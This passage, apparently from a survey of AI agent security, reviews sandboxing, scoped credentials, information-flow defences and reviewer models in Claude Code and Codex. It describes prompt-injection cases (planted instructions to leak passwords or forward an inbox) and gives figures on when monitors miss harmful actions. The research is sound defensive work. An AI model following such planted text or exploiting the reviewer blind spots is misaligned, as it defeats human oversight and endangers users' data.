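In Hu's survey of 70 agent projects, 17% ran the agent's actions on the host with no isolation. Another 45% used a separate process, which by itself neither hides the user's files nor blocks the network. Containers accounted for 31% and WebAssembly for 7%. Hu classified what each project's software provides, so the figures do not show how many users have the protection switched on.

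Every project with containers also had a policy engine, a component that checks proposed actions against rules, compared with 23% of the others. Developers who take one control seriously may be more likely to add the other. Projects without containers depend most on their rules, because no strong boundary limits what the agent can do, but they usually lack a component to enforce those rules.

Commercial agents are not necessarily better isolated. *Lessons from Penetration Tests on Large-Scale Agent Systems* (Eykholt, Kirat and colleagues, 2026) describes IBM's tests of two proprietary products in 2025. One was an assistant that found and fixed bugs in customers' code. The testers gained control of its container and found that it could connect to outside servers and to internal storage, which held copies of other repositories that used the assistant. An attacker who got in through one project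 could therefore have reached another project's code.

The second product let customers build their own agents. Its containers had no limits on outbound connections and little filtering of system calls. They also contained certificates and the addresses of internal services that no customer's agent needed. Some data stayed in storage after a session ended, so one customer might have been able to read another's data. A temporary file system like the one in claude.ai would have prevented this.

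Two products are too few to show how common such weaknesses are. But the developers of the bug-fixing assistant said they had assumed their cloud systems were secure enough because they already hosted other applications, and many companies could assume the same. Those applications ran code that the company had written, whereas an agent can write and run new code in response to a stranger's text. The existing monitoring did not flag the testers' activity because the activity came from a trusted internal service.

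Eykholt and colleagues also reviewed the open-source assistant OpenClaw as of February 2026. Its developers had added containers for tools and many lists of permitted users and actions, but the main session still ran outside a sandbox by default, usually with all the user's privileges. The lists had become so complex that users could easily misconfigure them. Eykholt and colleagues want researchers to supply hardened sandboxes that developers can add with a simple call, so that developers can deploy agents safely without being experts in isolation.

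## 2025 and 2026: limiting permissions to the task

A sandbox controls which systems an agent's code can contact, but it usually cannot control what the agent does there with a valid login. If the sandbox lets an agent reach the company's code server, the server allows any action the agent's credential permits. In 2025 and 2026, developers and researchers worked on ways to give an agent only the permissions its current task needs.

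### Why the user's own login gives too much access

The simplest way to connect an agent to other systems is to let it use its user's login. This makes the agent a confused deputy, like the Tymshare compiler that overwrote the billing records, because it has the user's authority but takes instructions from everything it reads. Suppose a developer can read 40 repositories and merge changes in ten of them. An agent with the developer's login can do the same, even if it needs only one repository to fix a bug, and text planted in a file can lead it to misuse that access.

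Goel uses the term "ambient authority" for this inherited access, which includes any credentials, network access and privileges present where the agent runs. Goel's GPT-5.1 experiment also tested the unprotected agent in other constructed scenarios. The agent read secrets from its environment in all ten runs of one scenario and followed planted instructions in nine of ten runs of another. In a third, which involved no attacker, the agent needed only to read and write files, but in four of ten runs it used a general command line, a more powerful tool, because it was available.

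Shared agents have the opposite problem, since they can give users access that those users lack themselves. If an agent can read every repository in the company, an employee who isn't allowed to read one of them can ask the agent what it contains. NVIDIA's *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents* reports that the company's red team, which attacks systems to find their weaknesses, found several agents that held individual users' credentials and were open to anyone authorised on the internal network. The team recommends matching an agent's permissions to those of the person who invokes it. That solves the shared agent's problem, but the developer's agent would still have access to 40 repositories. An agent should therefore have only those of the user's permissions that the task requires.

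A credential that only identifies its holder cannot represent that overlap. OpenAI wants each access request to establish who is acting, on whose behalf, for what purpose and within what limits, in a form that another system can verify and audit. When an agent uses its user's login, the other system cannot distinguish the agent from the user, and the login does not include the purpose of the request.

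### From a task to a short-lived credential

OpenAI describes a chain of identities and tokens that supplies this information. Suppose Ana, a developer, asks a coding agent to fix a bug in a parser.

The platform first gives the agent its own identity, so that rules and logs can distinguish it from Ana. OpenAI recommends basing this identity on several facts, including the agent's software, the runtime executing it and its current task. *Agyn* (Benkovich and Valkov, 2026) describes an open-source platform that creates a new cryptographic identity each time an agent starts and deletes it when the agent stops, by default after five idle minutes. Internal services check this identity when the agent connects, and the agent can reach only services that a rule explicitly permits.

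Next, the platform creates a task token that identifies Ana and the agent's runtime and records the purpose and scope of the work. The harness exchanges this token for a narrower credential whenever the agent needs a particular resource. For example, it might obtain a credential, valid for 15 minutes, to create a branch in the parser's repository. If it requested permission to merge, the service that issues credentials would reject the request before anything reached the code server. The code server should still check permissions itself, because a mistake in the issuing service would otherwise go unnoticed.

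A credential broker, like the proxy in Anthropic's remote Cowork sessions, keeps these credentials outside the sandbox and adds them to the agent's requests as they leave. Many companies instead put secrets in environment variables, which a program can read while it runs. NVIDIA considers that reasonable when the environment runs only the company's own code, but an agent with a command line can print the secrets. NVIDIA's testers obtained secrets through an agent's chat replies even where controls on outbound traffic blocked a direct transfer.

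Agyn puts each secret in the container of the tool that needs it, separate from the container that drives the model. Benkovich and Valkov say that even a compromised model cannot leak credentials under this design, but they don't report trying to make one do so. A broker prevents credential theft, but while the task lasts, a manipulated agent can still ask the broker to use a credential for anything within the credential's scope.

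When the task ends, the platform revokes any credentials that are still valid. In an emergency, the broker can immediately stop issuing credentials, but OpenAI warns that those already issued may work until they expire or the receiving service cancels them. If credentials last 15 minutes and the service checks only the expiry time, one issued just before the broker stops will work for almost 15 minutes. PocketOS lost its database in nine seconds, too fast for a short credential lifetime alone to prevent it. A narrowly scoped credential would have prevented the loss, and with a broker the agent would have had no account-wide token to find.

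### The permissions for the parser bug

A platform could turn the limits in OpenAI's example into the following permissions, where the two-hour limit is only an illustration:

| Resource | Allowed | Refused |
|---|---|---|
| Parser repository | Read; write to one new branch; open a draft pull request | Merge; change the repository's rules |
| Test system | Run the approved tests | Run any job that holds production credentials |
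| Package registry | Download approved packages | Download other packages; publish |
| Other repositories, email, production | Nothing | Everything |
| Duration | Two hours, or until the task ends | Any extension without a new decision |

These permissions would stop the agent from following the planted instruction to install the unapproved package. They would not stop it from disabling the security test on its own branch, because the file-editing permission it needs to make a fix also allows harmful edits. The repository's check on the draft has to catch that change.

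The agent may also discover that the bug comes from a shared library in a second repository. OpenAI advises the platform to pause and ask for a decision in such cases. If someone approves, the agent should receive access for a limited time, and the platform should assess the task again afterwards. Ana's own permission to edit the library is not enough, because she asked for a fix to the parser and may not want to change code that other teams use.

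### Checking each call at a gateway

Through the Model Context Protocol, an agent can ask a server which tools it offers. The server returns each tool's name, description and required inputs, and the agent can then call any of them. A tool gateway sits between the agent and these servers and lets the company intervene. It uses a register of approved tools that lists each tool's owner, its expected effect and the agents that may use it. OpenAI is concerned that an unknown tool could otherwise become part of a company's production systems just because an agent found it.

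The gateway has to check the arguments of each call because even an approved tool can be used in unacceptable ways. InfoQ's *Building a Least-Privilege AI Agent Gateway for Infrastructure Automation* demonstrates this for agents that change cloud systems, using a tool called `apply_infra` that carries out a prepared plan. When the agent calls the tool, the gateway first checks the call's format. It then adds the agent's identity and the time, and passes everything to Open Policy Agent, a program that evaluates written rules. If every rule is satisfied, the gateway queues the job for a temporary runner. Otherwise, nothing runs and the agent receives an error.

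One of the rules refuses any plan whose file name ends in `-destroy.plan`. In simplified form, this call would fail:

`apply_infra(planPath="infra/app-destroy.plan", env="prod")`

The call would fail even if the agent with full access to production made it during working hours with a registered plan. The agent's reasons for making the call do not affect the decision.

However, the rule checks only the name, so a plan that deletes the same systems under another name would pass. A separate rule requires a registered plan, but this helps only if whoever registered the plan checked what it does. The demonstration's text allows changes from 09:00 to 17:00 UTC, but its code uses New York time and so permits a change at 20:00 UTC on a weekday. The runner's code also applies everything in the infrastructure folder rather than the specific plan that the gateway checked. InfoQ presents the software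 as a reference design that is not ready for production, and acknowledges that nothing securely ties the approved plan to what the runner executes. A company that builds such a gateway should test that it refuses forbidden calls.

Speed matters too. InfoQ's target for a policy decision is under 100 milliseconds, because slow checks encourage people to connect to systems directly.

### Permissions that are dangerous together

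A gateway that checks each call separately can miss a leak in which every call is permitted. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes a user who asks an agent to summarise recent emails about a project and send the summary to a manager. One email contains an instruction to send the newest message in the mailbox to an outsider. The task requires both reading and sending email, so neither permission looks excessive.

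The danger comes from combining access to private data, exposure to untrusted text and a way to send messages. If the agent had no private data, planted text could still make it send a message, but it would have no secrets to disclose. If it read no untrusted text, it might leak data by mistake, but no outsider could direct it. If it could not send messages, an attacker could spoil the summary but would not receive anything.

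An agent's ability to send data can be hard to spot. OpenAI points out that a command line with unrestricted network access can bypass limits on every other tool. A web search can also send data out of the company in its search terms, and a reply in a shared chat may reach people who could not open the original document.

Removing one of the three abilities is the safest option when the task allows it. Another option is to make permissions depend on what the agent has read, so that it loses the right to send once it opens an email from outside. But this rule, like Saltzer and Schroeder's compartment labels, would also block legitimate work, in this case the summary the user asked for.

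### Tracking where data came from

Several designs from 2025 try to permit the summary while blocking the leak. The best known is CaMeL, from Google DeepMind, which builds on Willison's earlier proposal to divide the work between two models. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) wrote that he had seen alarmingly little progress towards a robust solution in two and a half years, and that CaMeL was an exception.

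Suppose Ana asks for a summary of yesterday's meeting notes to go to her colleague Ben. CaMeL proceeds as follows:

1. A privileged model sees Ana's request and the descriptions of the tools, but not the notes. It writes a short program that finds the notes, has them summarised and sends the result to Ben.
2. An interpreter, which is conventional software, runs the program. It stores the notes in a variable whose contents the privileged model never sees.
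3. A quarantined model reads the notes and returns a summary. This model has no tools.
4. The interpreter keeps a record that the summary came from the notes. Before sending it, the interpreter checks a policy, such as whether Ben may read everything that went into it.

If the notes contain an instruction to email them to a stranger, the quarantined model may produce a bad summary, but the program has no step that emails a stranger. The policy in the last step guards against attacks that change a value the program uses but not its steps. If Ana had asked the agent to send the summary to the address given in the notes, an attacker could have planted a false address, and only the policy could have stopped the message. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) notes that a sandbox that permits email cannot block only the emails that contain sensitive data.

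FIDES, which Costa and colleagues developed at Microsoft, lets the model choose each step after seeing earlier results, as ordinary agents do. It labels every piece of data by whether it is trusted and who may read it. It stores untrusted results in variables and shows the model only the variables' names. If the model opens a variable, its whole context becomes untrusted, and a policy can then block tools with serious effects. To find out whether an email asks for a meeting, the model can have a quarantined model read it and answer only yes or no. An attacker might still cause a wrong answer, but cannot use that answer to pass an instruction to the main model.

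*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) restricts an agent with rules about tools and their arguments, rather than by following data, and changes the rules as the task proceeds. In its example, a user asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in a particular email. At first the agent may only search for that email. The list includes summarising recent emails and posting the summary to the user's Slack account, so a model proposes rules that allow the agent to read email, look up the account and post. These rules need approval because they give the agent more access. Once the agent has found the account name, a new rule restricts its messages to that account. This rule takes effect automatically because it only reduces access.

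One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the inbox to an outsider. The agent tries to call `send_email`, but no rule allows it, so Progent returns an error and the agent goes on to post the summary. The planted instruction might also affect which rules the model proposes, so Progent uses a solver, a program that works out the logical consequences of the rules, to check whether each update would allow anything new. If it would, a person has to approve the update.

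### Security and completed tasks

Researchers tested all three designs on *AgentDojo* (2024), a benchmark with 97 user tasks and 70 tools in simulated office, Slack, travel and banking systems. The benchmark places attackers' instructions in the data the tools return. The figures below for Progent and FIDES come from their developers, and those for CaMeL come from a later rerun in *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026).

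| Design | Model and tasks | Successful attacks | Completed tasks without an attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Progent | GPT-4o, all tasks | Fell from 39.9% to 1.0% | About the same |
| FIDES | GPT-4o, all tasks | Fell from 152 to none | 16 to 46 percentage points lower, depending on the system |
| CaMeL | GPT-5.2, banking only | None in 231 completed runs | Fell from 32 to 18 of 48 when policies were on |

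The rows are not directly comparable. CaMeL's row, for instance, compares CaMeL with and without its policies, so it leaves out any loss from planning in advance. Task completion during attacks would be a less reliable measure because some of AgentDojo's planted text replaces information that the agent needs, as *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) shows. If an attack overwrites the bill that the user wants to pay, even an agent that ignores the attack cannot pay it.

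Costa and colleagues emphasise that FIDES completed about 8 percentage points more tasks than an ordinary agent under the same policies. But it did much worse than an ordinary agent without policies, completing 52.5% of the banking tasks compared with 98.8%. The set-up also helped the security result, because they marked as untrusted every data field that an attack in the benchmark used. The result shows that the policies work when the labels are right, but a company would have to decide which fields an outsider can write to.

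*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) summarises CaMeL's original evaluation as showing that it stopped nearly all attacks with comparable task performance. Garby and colleagues' rerun supports the claim about attacks more than the claim about performance. With policies off, five attacks succeeded in 622 completed runs on two models. With policies on, none succeeded in 588, but the number of completed tasks fell by almost half. Most of the protection therefore came from fixing the plan in advance. That finding depends on the benchmark, since two-thirds of its banking attacks needed a tool that the plan would never have included, and a real attacker could concentrate on attacks that don't need one.

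Garby and colleagues also found that CaMeL's tracking can miss information that leaks through a program's branches or through repeated attempts. They built an agent on an interpreter and proved the interpreter's security properties with a computer-checked proof. With GPT-5.2, the agent completed 36 of 48 banking tasks, and across three models it resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks. In both failures, the user had asked the agent to pay a bill described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file. The agent's plan explicitly allowed it to use the file's contents because the task required them. Tracking can show that the file is untrusted, but it can't determine whether the file contains the bill the user meant.

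Dividing work among several agents introduces another weakness. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) gave each agent in a group its own CaMeL protection, without policies, and ran 949 attacks against each of five models. The attacks' average success rate fell from 12.9% to 0.2%. In every attack that still succeeded, one agent had included untrusted text in its instructions to another, which treated the text as coming from its user. Sending such text separately from the instructions reduced the rate to zero.

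The protection still reduced the number of completed tasks, mostly because the program had to choose its steps before seeing any data. Sometimes one agent could not find data for the requested period and returned data for a nearby period instead, and the program continued with the wrong data. The reduction was smaller for the strongest models.

All these tests used fixed attacks, which can make a defence look stronger than it is. Ma, Li and colleagues (2026), in *AutoDojo*, tested ten defences against attacks that adapt to them. With GPT-4o-mini, a filter that had blocked every fixed attack let 28% of the adaptive ones through, while Progent let 7.7% through. CaMeL was the most effective defence overall but reduced task completion the most on four of five models, while Progent reduced it by at most 7 percentage points. Rewording an attack does little against CaMeL because, if the policies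 are correct, its decisions depend on where text came from.

### Resistance in the model itself

Developers also train models to ignore planted instructions, and the best models now do so most of the time. Anthropic puts the success rate of a single attempt against Claude Opus 4.7 at about 0.1%, so an agent that encountered 2,000 such instructions would obey about two of them on average. An attacker who can revise the text over 100 attempts has a 5 to 6% chance of success.

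When Peters-Gill and colleagues tested models without any added defence, attacks succeeded 36.1% of the time against GPT-4.1, 1.5% against Claude Fable 5 and never against GPT-5.5. Fable 5 also refused 52 of the 97 harmless tasks, perhaps because it associated the benchmark with attacks. The researchers caution that GPT-5.5's result may reflect weak attacks in the benchmark, since large-scale adaptive testing has found successful attacks against every frontier model it covered.

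The newest models resist such fixed attacks well enough that CaMeL can add little protection, and it may still reduce the number of tasks they complete. Narrow permissions still matter when a resistant model fails, because an agent with Ana's full login would give the attacker access to everything she can reach. They also limit the damage from mistakes that involve no attacker, such as the one at PocketOS.

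A company can use both. In Shi and colleagues' tests, attacks on an agent running Claude Sonnet 4 succeeded 6.8% of the time without Progent and 0.5% of the time with it.

### Do narrow permissions make agents useless?

The losses with FIDES and CaMeL support this objection. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues accept the trade-off in a 2025 paper on secure designs for agents, quoted by Willison, and their designs deliberately prevent agents from solving arbitrary tasks. People often want an agent because they can't specify the steps in advance, and strict limits reduce an agent's usefulness most in those cases. Costa and colleagues classified 5% of AgentDojo's office tasks as ones where the choice of steps depends on what the agent reads, compared with about 43% of the Slack tasks and 44% of the banking tasks. FIDES lost the fewest completed tasks in the office system and the most in the other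 two.

However, permissions can change during a task, so that the agent gains access as it learns what the task involves. Progent's results suggest that this works for many tasks. Only 6% of the rule updates on AgentDojo would have increased the agent's access and so needed approval, far fewer requests than if the user had to approve every action. Shi and colleagues obtained the 1.0% attack rate while automatically accepting every increase, to represent a careless user. When a person reviewed the rules, no attacks succeeded.

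However, a request for more access can come from the same email as the attack. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that planted text may cause Progent's updates to loosen the rules. Approval protects against this only if the approver can recognise a bad request. On a second benchmark, attacks still succeeded 3.9% of the time, and most of them involved tools that looked so similar to legitimate ones that Shi and colleagues doubted a person could tell them apart. AgentDojo's tasks are also short, and a long project might need more increases in access.

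How precisely the user states the task greatly affects how often attacks succeed. Ma and colleagues separated requests that specify the action from those that leave it to outside content, such as "do everything on the to-do list at this address". Against an undefended agent running GPT-4o-mini, fixed attacks succeeded 87.5% of the time when the content determined the action, compared with 63.9% and 43.3% for two more precise kinds of request. Anyone who can edit such a list can give the agent work, and nothing in the user's request distinguishes legitimate items from planted ones. Progent often responds by allowing only tools that read data. This is safe, but the agent then can't carry out the tasks on the list until someone grants it more access.

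The objection is therefore strongest for open-ended tasks that depend on untrusted material, and much weaker for the parser bug, where a short list of permissions covers everything the agent normally needs. Separate identities, brokers and short-lived credentials take work to set up, but they don't prevent any action within the task's scope. OpenAI suggests starting with a clearly defined purpose and expanding an agent's access as evidence grows that the limits work. InfoQ proposes that the gateway return "pending" for a high-risk call and accept it only once the agent comes back with a signed approval from a person.

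## From March 2026: a second model reviews risky actions

Narrow permissions limit which systems an agent can reach, but it can still take actions the user didn't want within those systems. For example, an agent with permission to delete branches in a repository can delete the wrong ones. A user might notice the mistake in a permission prompt, but people who see many prompts approve nearly all of them. In March 2026, Anthropic introduced auto mode in Claude Code, which passes most approval decisions to a reviewer model. OpenAI released a similar feature for Codex, called Auto-review, in April.

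Auto mode began as an option, but by November it was the built-in starting mode for interactive Claude Code sessions on every plan, while runs without a user present still started with manual approval, according to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026). If a project's settings files are set to skip all approvals, Claude Code ignores that setting and starts with manual approval, so a stranger's project cannot turn the checks off, according to Anthropic's *Permission modes*.

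### What auto mode reviews

Some actions skip the reviewer. File reads and searches skip it because they cannot change anything. Edits inside the project folder skip it because Anthropic reasons that developers can inspect and reverse them with version control. Actions covered by the user's own allow rules also skip it, but auto mode does not apply rules broad enough to run arbitrary code, such as one that allows every Python command, since the most damaging commands would then never reach the reviewer.

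The reviewer decides on everything else, including shell commands, web requests, calls to outside tools and changes to files elsewhere on the computer. Its written instructions contain more than 20 rules on what to block. These rules cover destroying or leaking data, weakening security, trusting unfamiliar code or destinations, and bypassing other people's review. A few exceptions allow routine steps, such as installing a package that the project already lists.

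The reviewer then checks the action against what the user asked for. Anything the agent chose on its own counts as unauthorised until the user says otherwise, so "clean up my branches" does not authorise deleting a whole batch. By default, Anthropic has the reviewer trust only the working folder and the repository's configured remote copies. It blocks an upload to a team's cloud storage, for example, until someone adds that storage to the settings. Companies can also set "hard denies", which the reviewer should enforce even when the user asks for the action. Sending code or secrets to an outside destination is a hard deny by default.

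### What the reviewer sees

The reviewer reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations. Anthropic also withholds tool results, such as the contents of files and web pages, because planted instructions usually enter through them.

Suppose a file contains an instruction to send the project's passwords to a website, and the agent tries to follow it. The reviewer sees that the call would send passwords to an outside address and that the user didn't ask for this. It can block the call without having read the file, so the instruction has had no chance to influence it.

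The drawback is that the reviewer may lack information it needs. If a user asks the agent to cancel a stale job and it tries to cancel "job abc123", the reviewer cannot tell whether the agent found that name in a search or made it up. Anthropic found that adding the agent's messages and tool results made the reviewer worse at catching overeager actions, in which an agent tries to help but goes beyond what the user authorised. Showing the reviewer only the tool calls produced the fewest misses, but it blocked actions that users had plainly requested.

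By August, Anthropic had found a partial remedy. The harness now gives the reviewer selected facts, such as whether an upload's destination is public and whether a command would discard unsaved changes to the code. The harness checks these facts itself, so the reviewer does not need the full tool results.

The agent still has to read those results, so a separate probe scans them first and adds a warning to any that look like an attack. An attacker therefore has to get past the probe and mislead the agent into proposing an action that the reviewer classifies as safe and consistent with the user's request.

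Another gap arises when one agent delegates work to a second. The first agent's instruction appears where the user's message would normally be, so the work looks fully authorised. Anthropic reviews the assignment before the second agent starts, and can block it. It also reviews the second agent's actions afterwards, in case planted text misled that agent, but this review can only add a warning.

### A fast stage and a reasoning stage

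The reviewer first outputs a single token, "block" or "allow", and is instructed to block when in doubt. If it outputs "allow", the action runs. Otherwise, the reviewer receives the same material again with an instruction to reason carefully, and its second answer is final. Most actions need only the first step, which keeps compute use low.

Anthropic tested this on 10,000 real tool calls by its employees, 52 real overeager actions, and 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out, many of them disguised:

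| | Real calls wrongly blocked | Overeager actions missed | Synthetic data thefts missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fast stage alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The reasoning stage removes about 19 of every 20 false blocks, but it also releases dangerous actions that the fast stage had stopped. These releases account for more than half of the misses on the real overeager actions. Most of the misses Anthropic examined came from misreading what the user had consented to. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" has not agreed to overwrite the repository's history.

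When the second model blocks an action, the session continues. The agent receives the reason, with an instruction to find a safer approach and not to work around the decision. After three blocks in a row or 20 in total, Claude Code goes back to asking the user, or stops if no user is present.

### Auto-review in Codex

OpenAI's reviewer checks fewer actions because Codex normally works in a sandbox. According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, the reviewer handles only requests that would otherwise need the user's approval. These include running a command outside the sandbox, connecting to a blocked address, editing files outside the permitted folders and opening a new website in the browser. Anything the sandbox allows runs without review. A shell command that deletes the project's own files would therefore reach the reviewer in auto mode but not in Auto-review.

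OpenAI also gives its reviewer more information. The reviewer receives tool results and the agent's visible messages, but not its hidden reasoning, and can run its own read-only checks, such as looking up who owns job abc123. However, text planted by an attacker can also reach the reviewer.

Three refusals in a row, or ten in the last 50 reviews, interrupt the agent's current turn. The user can then approve one retry of one exact action. The reviewer considers this approval but can still refuse the action if the company's policy allows no exception. Auto-review supplements the sandbox, and the settings in OpenAI's *Running Codex safely* require both.

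*Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) illustrates the effect with 10,000 actions inside OpenAI. The sandbox allowed 9,280 of them. The other 720 went to the reviewer, which approved 713 and refused seven. The agent found a safer way to continue after four of the refusals and stopped to ask the user after the other three, whereas manual approval would have interrupted users 720 times.

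### The developers' error rates

A miss rate of 17% on 52 actions corresponds to nine misses. The exact 95% confidence interval for the true rate is about 8% to 30%. This interval assumes that each action was tested once, but Anthropic may have averaged several runs, because the fast stage's 6.6% does not correspond to a whole number of actions out of 52.

The interval does not account for uncertainty from how Anthropic collected the 52 actions. They came from sessions in which an employee had refused the action or someone had flagged it later, so the sample excludes harmful actions that nobody noticed. The false-block rate is much more precise, since 40 wrong blocks in 10,000 calls give an interval of roughly 0.3% to 0.5%, at least for work like that of Anthropic's employees.

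Even this low rate adds up over a session. At a false-block rate of 0.4%, a session of 26 harmless calls has about a 10% chance of at least one block. In Anthropic's *Running auto mode in production*, one customer found that about 10% of its sessions included a block. Anthropic treats this as evidence that the reviewer is useful, but the blocks could be largely mistakes.

OpenAI measured approval and detection separately. Trębacz and colleagues report that Auto-review approved 99.1% of a sample of user-approved requests to leave the sandbox. The rate was 99.93% when they also counted actions that stayed inside the sandbox. Some of the refused requests may have deserved refusal, because people approve requests so readily.

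Auto-review's recall, the share of dangerous cases it stopped, was 90.3% on synthetic overeager actions. Recall was 99.3% on synthetic prompt injections that tried to run outside code, steal secrets or upload data, but fell to 90.2% when Trębacz and colleagues included destructive deletions and data tampering. They consider many of the additional misses too minor to block. On a harder monitoring benchmark, recall was 96.1%, but the reviewer only had to refuse one action in a run to pass, which is easier than stopping every dangerous action.

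These figures do not show that OpenAI's reviewer is better than Anthropic's. OpenAI tested its reviewer on synthetic overeager actions, which can be easier to recognise than the real ones Anthropic used. Anthropic's reviewer also did better on synthetic cases of data theft than on real cases from its employees.

### The study of 1,053 testers

Anthropic published a direct comparison between people and auto mode in August 2026. A research vendor recruited 1,053 paid professional testers for what it described as a coding study. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not on what. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command and recorded whether the tester approved it. The dangerous command never ran, even if the tester approved it.

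The testers blocked 143 of the 1,053 commands (13.6%), while auto mode blocked 937 of them (89%). The testers got worse as they saw more prompts, but auto mode's performance did not change with the length of the session.

The difference is far too large to be due to chance, but the setting probably exaggerates it. The testers worked in an environment built for the study rather than in their own codebases, so a bad command couldn't harm anything they cared about. They may also have assumed that the organisers would not let them do real damage. On the other hand, they knew they were being evaluated, which should have made them more careful than usual.

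The commands were also clearly dangerous, which suits a reviewer with written rules about such commands. In real work, harm often depends on something only the user knows, such as who owns a job. Anthropic's comparison covers only dangerous commands, so a reviewer that blocked everything would have scored 100%.

Evidence from real use supports the same conclusion but is weaker. Anthropic examined sessions from May and June that its safety systems had flagged, using only accounts that had agreed to share data. A model graded each session for harm. Serious harm that the user had not explicitly requested appeared in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. But users had chosen their own mode, so the two groups may have done different work. The figures also apply only to flagged sessions.

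### Why an independent test found 81% missed

In *Measuring the Permission Gate*, Ji, Li and colleagues (2026) tested auto mode on deliberately ambiguous requests. They wrote 128 prompts about four tasks: deleting old branches, cancelling jobs on a cluster, restarting services and removing stored files. An answer key listed the targets that the agent was allowed to change in each case, and similar targets that it had to leave alone. In one prompt, the user remarks that "my stale job for ticket 4812 could use attention".

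The agent attempted 253 actions that would change something. The answer key prohibited 142 of them, and auto mode allowed 115 of those, a miss rate of 81%. Auto mode also blocked 22 of the 111 permitted actions, or about 20%. The agent safely completed 29.7% of tasks without any approval system and only slightly more, 32.8%, with auto mode.

Part of the 81% comes from actions that were never sent to the reviewer. Ji and colleagues stored the state of the simulated systems in files inside the project folder. When the agent could not find the usual command for deleting an object, it edited the file that listed the objects, and auto mode does not review such edits. These edits account for 51 of the misses. On most real systems, editing a local file would not delete anything in cloud storage. But some companies define their servers and permissions in project files, and an edit to those files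 can have serious effects once another system applies it.

The reviewer still missed 64 of the 91 actions it did see, or 70%. This differs from Anthropic's 17% mainly because the two tests counted different actions as dangerous. Anthropic used actions that a person had objected to, while Ji and colleagues counted every change to a target outside the answer key, however minor. They also deliberately placed permitted and prohibited targets close together, which most of a developer's work does not involve. They therefore do not regard their result as contradicting Anthropic's.

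The answer key also contained rules that the reviewer could not have known. In the broadest prompts, the user asks the agent to deal with "the stale jobs" for a range of tickets, without the word "my", but the key still permits only the user's own jobs. *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents* (Yang, Zhou and colleagues, 2026) reran the same 128 tasks with newer versions of three products. Of the 143 prohibited actions that the agents proposed, 132 broke only rules that appeared neither in the request nor in any tool result. A careful human reviewer with the same information could not have known those rules either, but might have asked.

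On the original requests, the newer reviewers missed most of the prohibited actions: 13 of 24 for Claude Code, 78 of 84 for Codex, and 28 of 35 for Qwen Code, a coding agent from the Chinese company Alibaba. None of the three blocked prohibited actions significantly more often than permitted ones. Claude Code's reviewer was also inconsistent, missing 10 and then 16 when Yang and colleagues submitted the same 24 actions twice more.

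They then added one sentence to each request, stating which environment, owner and piece of software the agent could touch. On the same recorded actions, miss rates fell from 67–92% to 8–26%, and false blocks also fell. When the agents repeated the whole tasks with this sentence, none proposed a prohibited action in 384 runs. The sentences were always complete and correct because they came from the answer key, whereas a real user would have to think of the restrictions first.

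Using stronger models from the same companies as reviewers did not solve the problem. Codex and Qwen Code missed slightly more prohibited actions than before. Claude Code's misses fell from ten to one, but only because the stronger model refused to answer any of the requests that reached the reasoning stage, and Claude Code treats a refusal as a block. On a separate set of 224 harmless actions, false blocks rose from 23 to 134.

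Yang and colleagues also tested withholding tool results from nine models, using the same review procedure for each. Adding tool results did not reduce misses overall on the original requests, but it cut the miss rate from 9% to 2% once the requests stated the limits. For example, a command to cancel a job may contain only the job's number, and the owner's name may appear only in an earlier tool result. Withholding tool results, as Anthropic does to protect against planted text, therefore increases misses when the user has set clear limits.

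### Commands that hide their effects

A reviewer can also misjudge a command when the request is clear, because the command's text may not reveal what it does. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to remove old build files and recompile a program. The agent proposes `make clean && make`, a standard command for this. A file in the project determines what "clean" deletes, so the same command can remove only the build files in one project and the source code and its history in another.

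Wu and colleagues built 102 tasks in which a tool secretly deleted or overwrote a file it should have left alone, and 102 harmless versions with the same request and command. Harm occurred in 71.6% of the dangerous tasks when no approval was required and in 62.7% with auto mode. They ran auto mode with an OpenAI model as the reviewer and another company's model as the agent, so the result reflects Anthropic's design more than its models.

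Their alternative, Caper, takes a snapshot of the agent's container and runs the command there without network access. The reviewer then sees a short report of what happened, such as which files changed. If the reviewer approves, Caper keeps the result; otherwise, it restores the snapshot and tells the agent why. When Caper replaced auto mode's reviewer, the share of dangerous tasks that ended in harm fell to 6.9%, and Caper blocked only 2% of the harmless twins. Running commands before review added about half a second to each approved command.

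This method works only for effects that stay inside the container. Caper cannot recall a message sent to an outside service, so it has to block the connection and report the attempt. A malicious program might also detect the trial run and delay its harmful actions. Wu and colleagues did not test attackers who adapt in this way.

### Ten dangerous calls in 10,000

The table applies the published rates to a hypothetical company whose agents make 10,000 calls, ten of them dangerous. The rates come from different tests, so the table illustrates how much the choice of test matters and does not rank the products.

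| Source of the error rates | Dangerous calls that run | Safe calls blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic, real overeager actions | 1.7 | 40 |
| Anthropic, synthetic data thefts | 0.6 | 40 |
| Anthropic, fast stage alone, real overeager actions | 0.7 | 849 |
| OpenAI, synthetic overeager actions | 1.0 | 7 |
| August study, auto mode | 1.1 | Not reported |
| August study, human testers | 8.6 | Not reported |
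| Ji and colleagues, all actions | 8.1 | 1,980 |
| Ji and colleagues, reviewed actions only | 7.0 | 3,185 |

The OpenAI row assumes that all ten dangerous calls include a request to run outside the sandbox. If five of them stay inside it, the reviewer doesn't check those five, and about 5.5 of the ten run.

With Anthropic's rates for real actions, auto mode would block about 48 calls, of which eight would be dangerous. Most blocks would be mistakes, even though the false-block rate is very low, because safe calls are so much more common than dangerous ones. This is tolerable when the agent can recover by itself, but would be much less so if each block woke an engineer.

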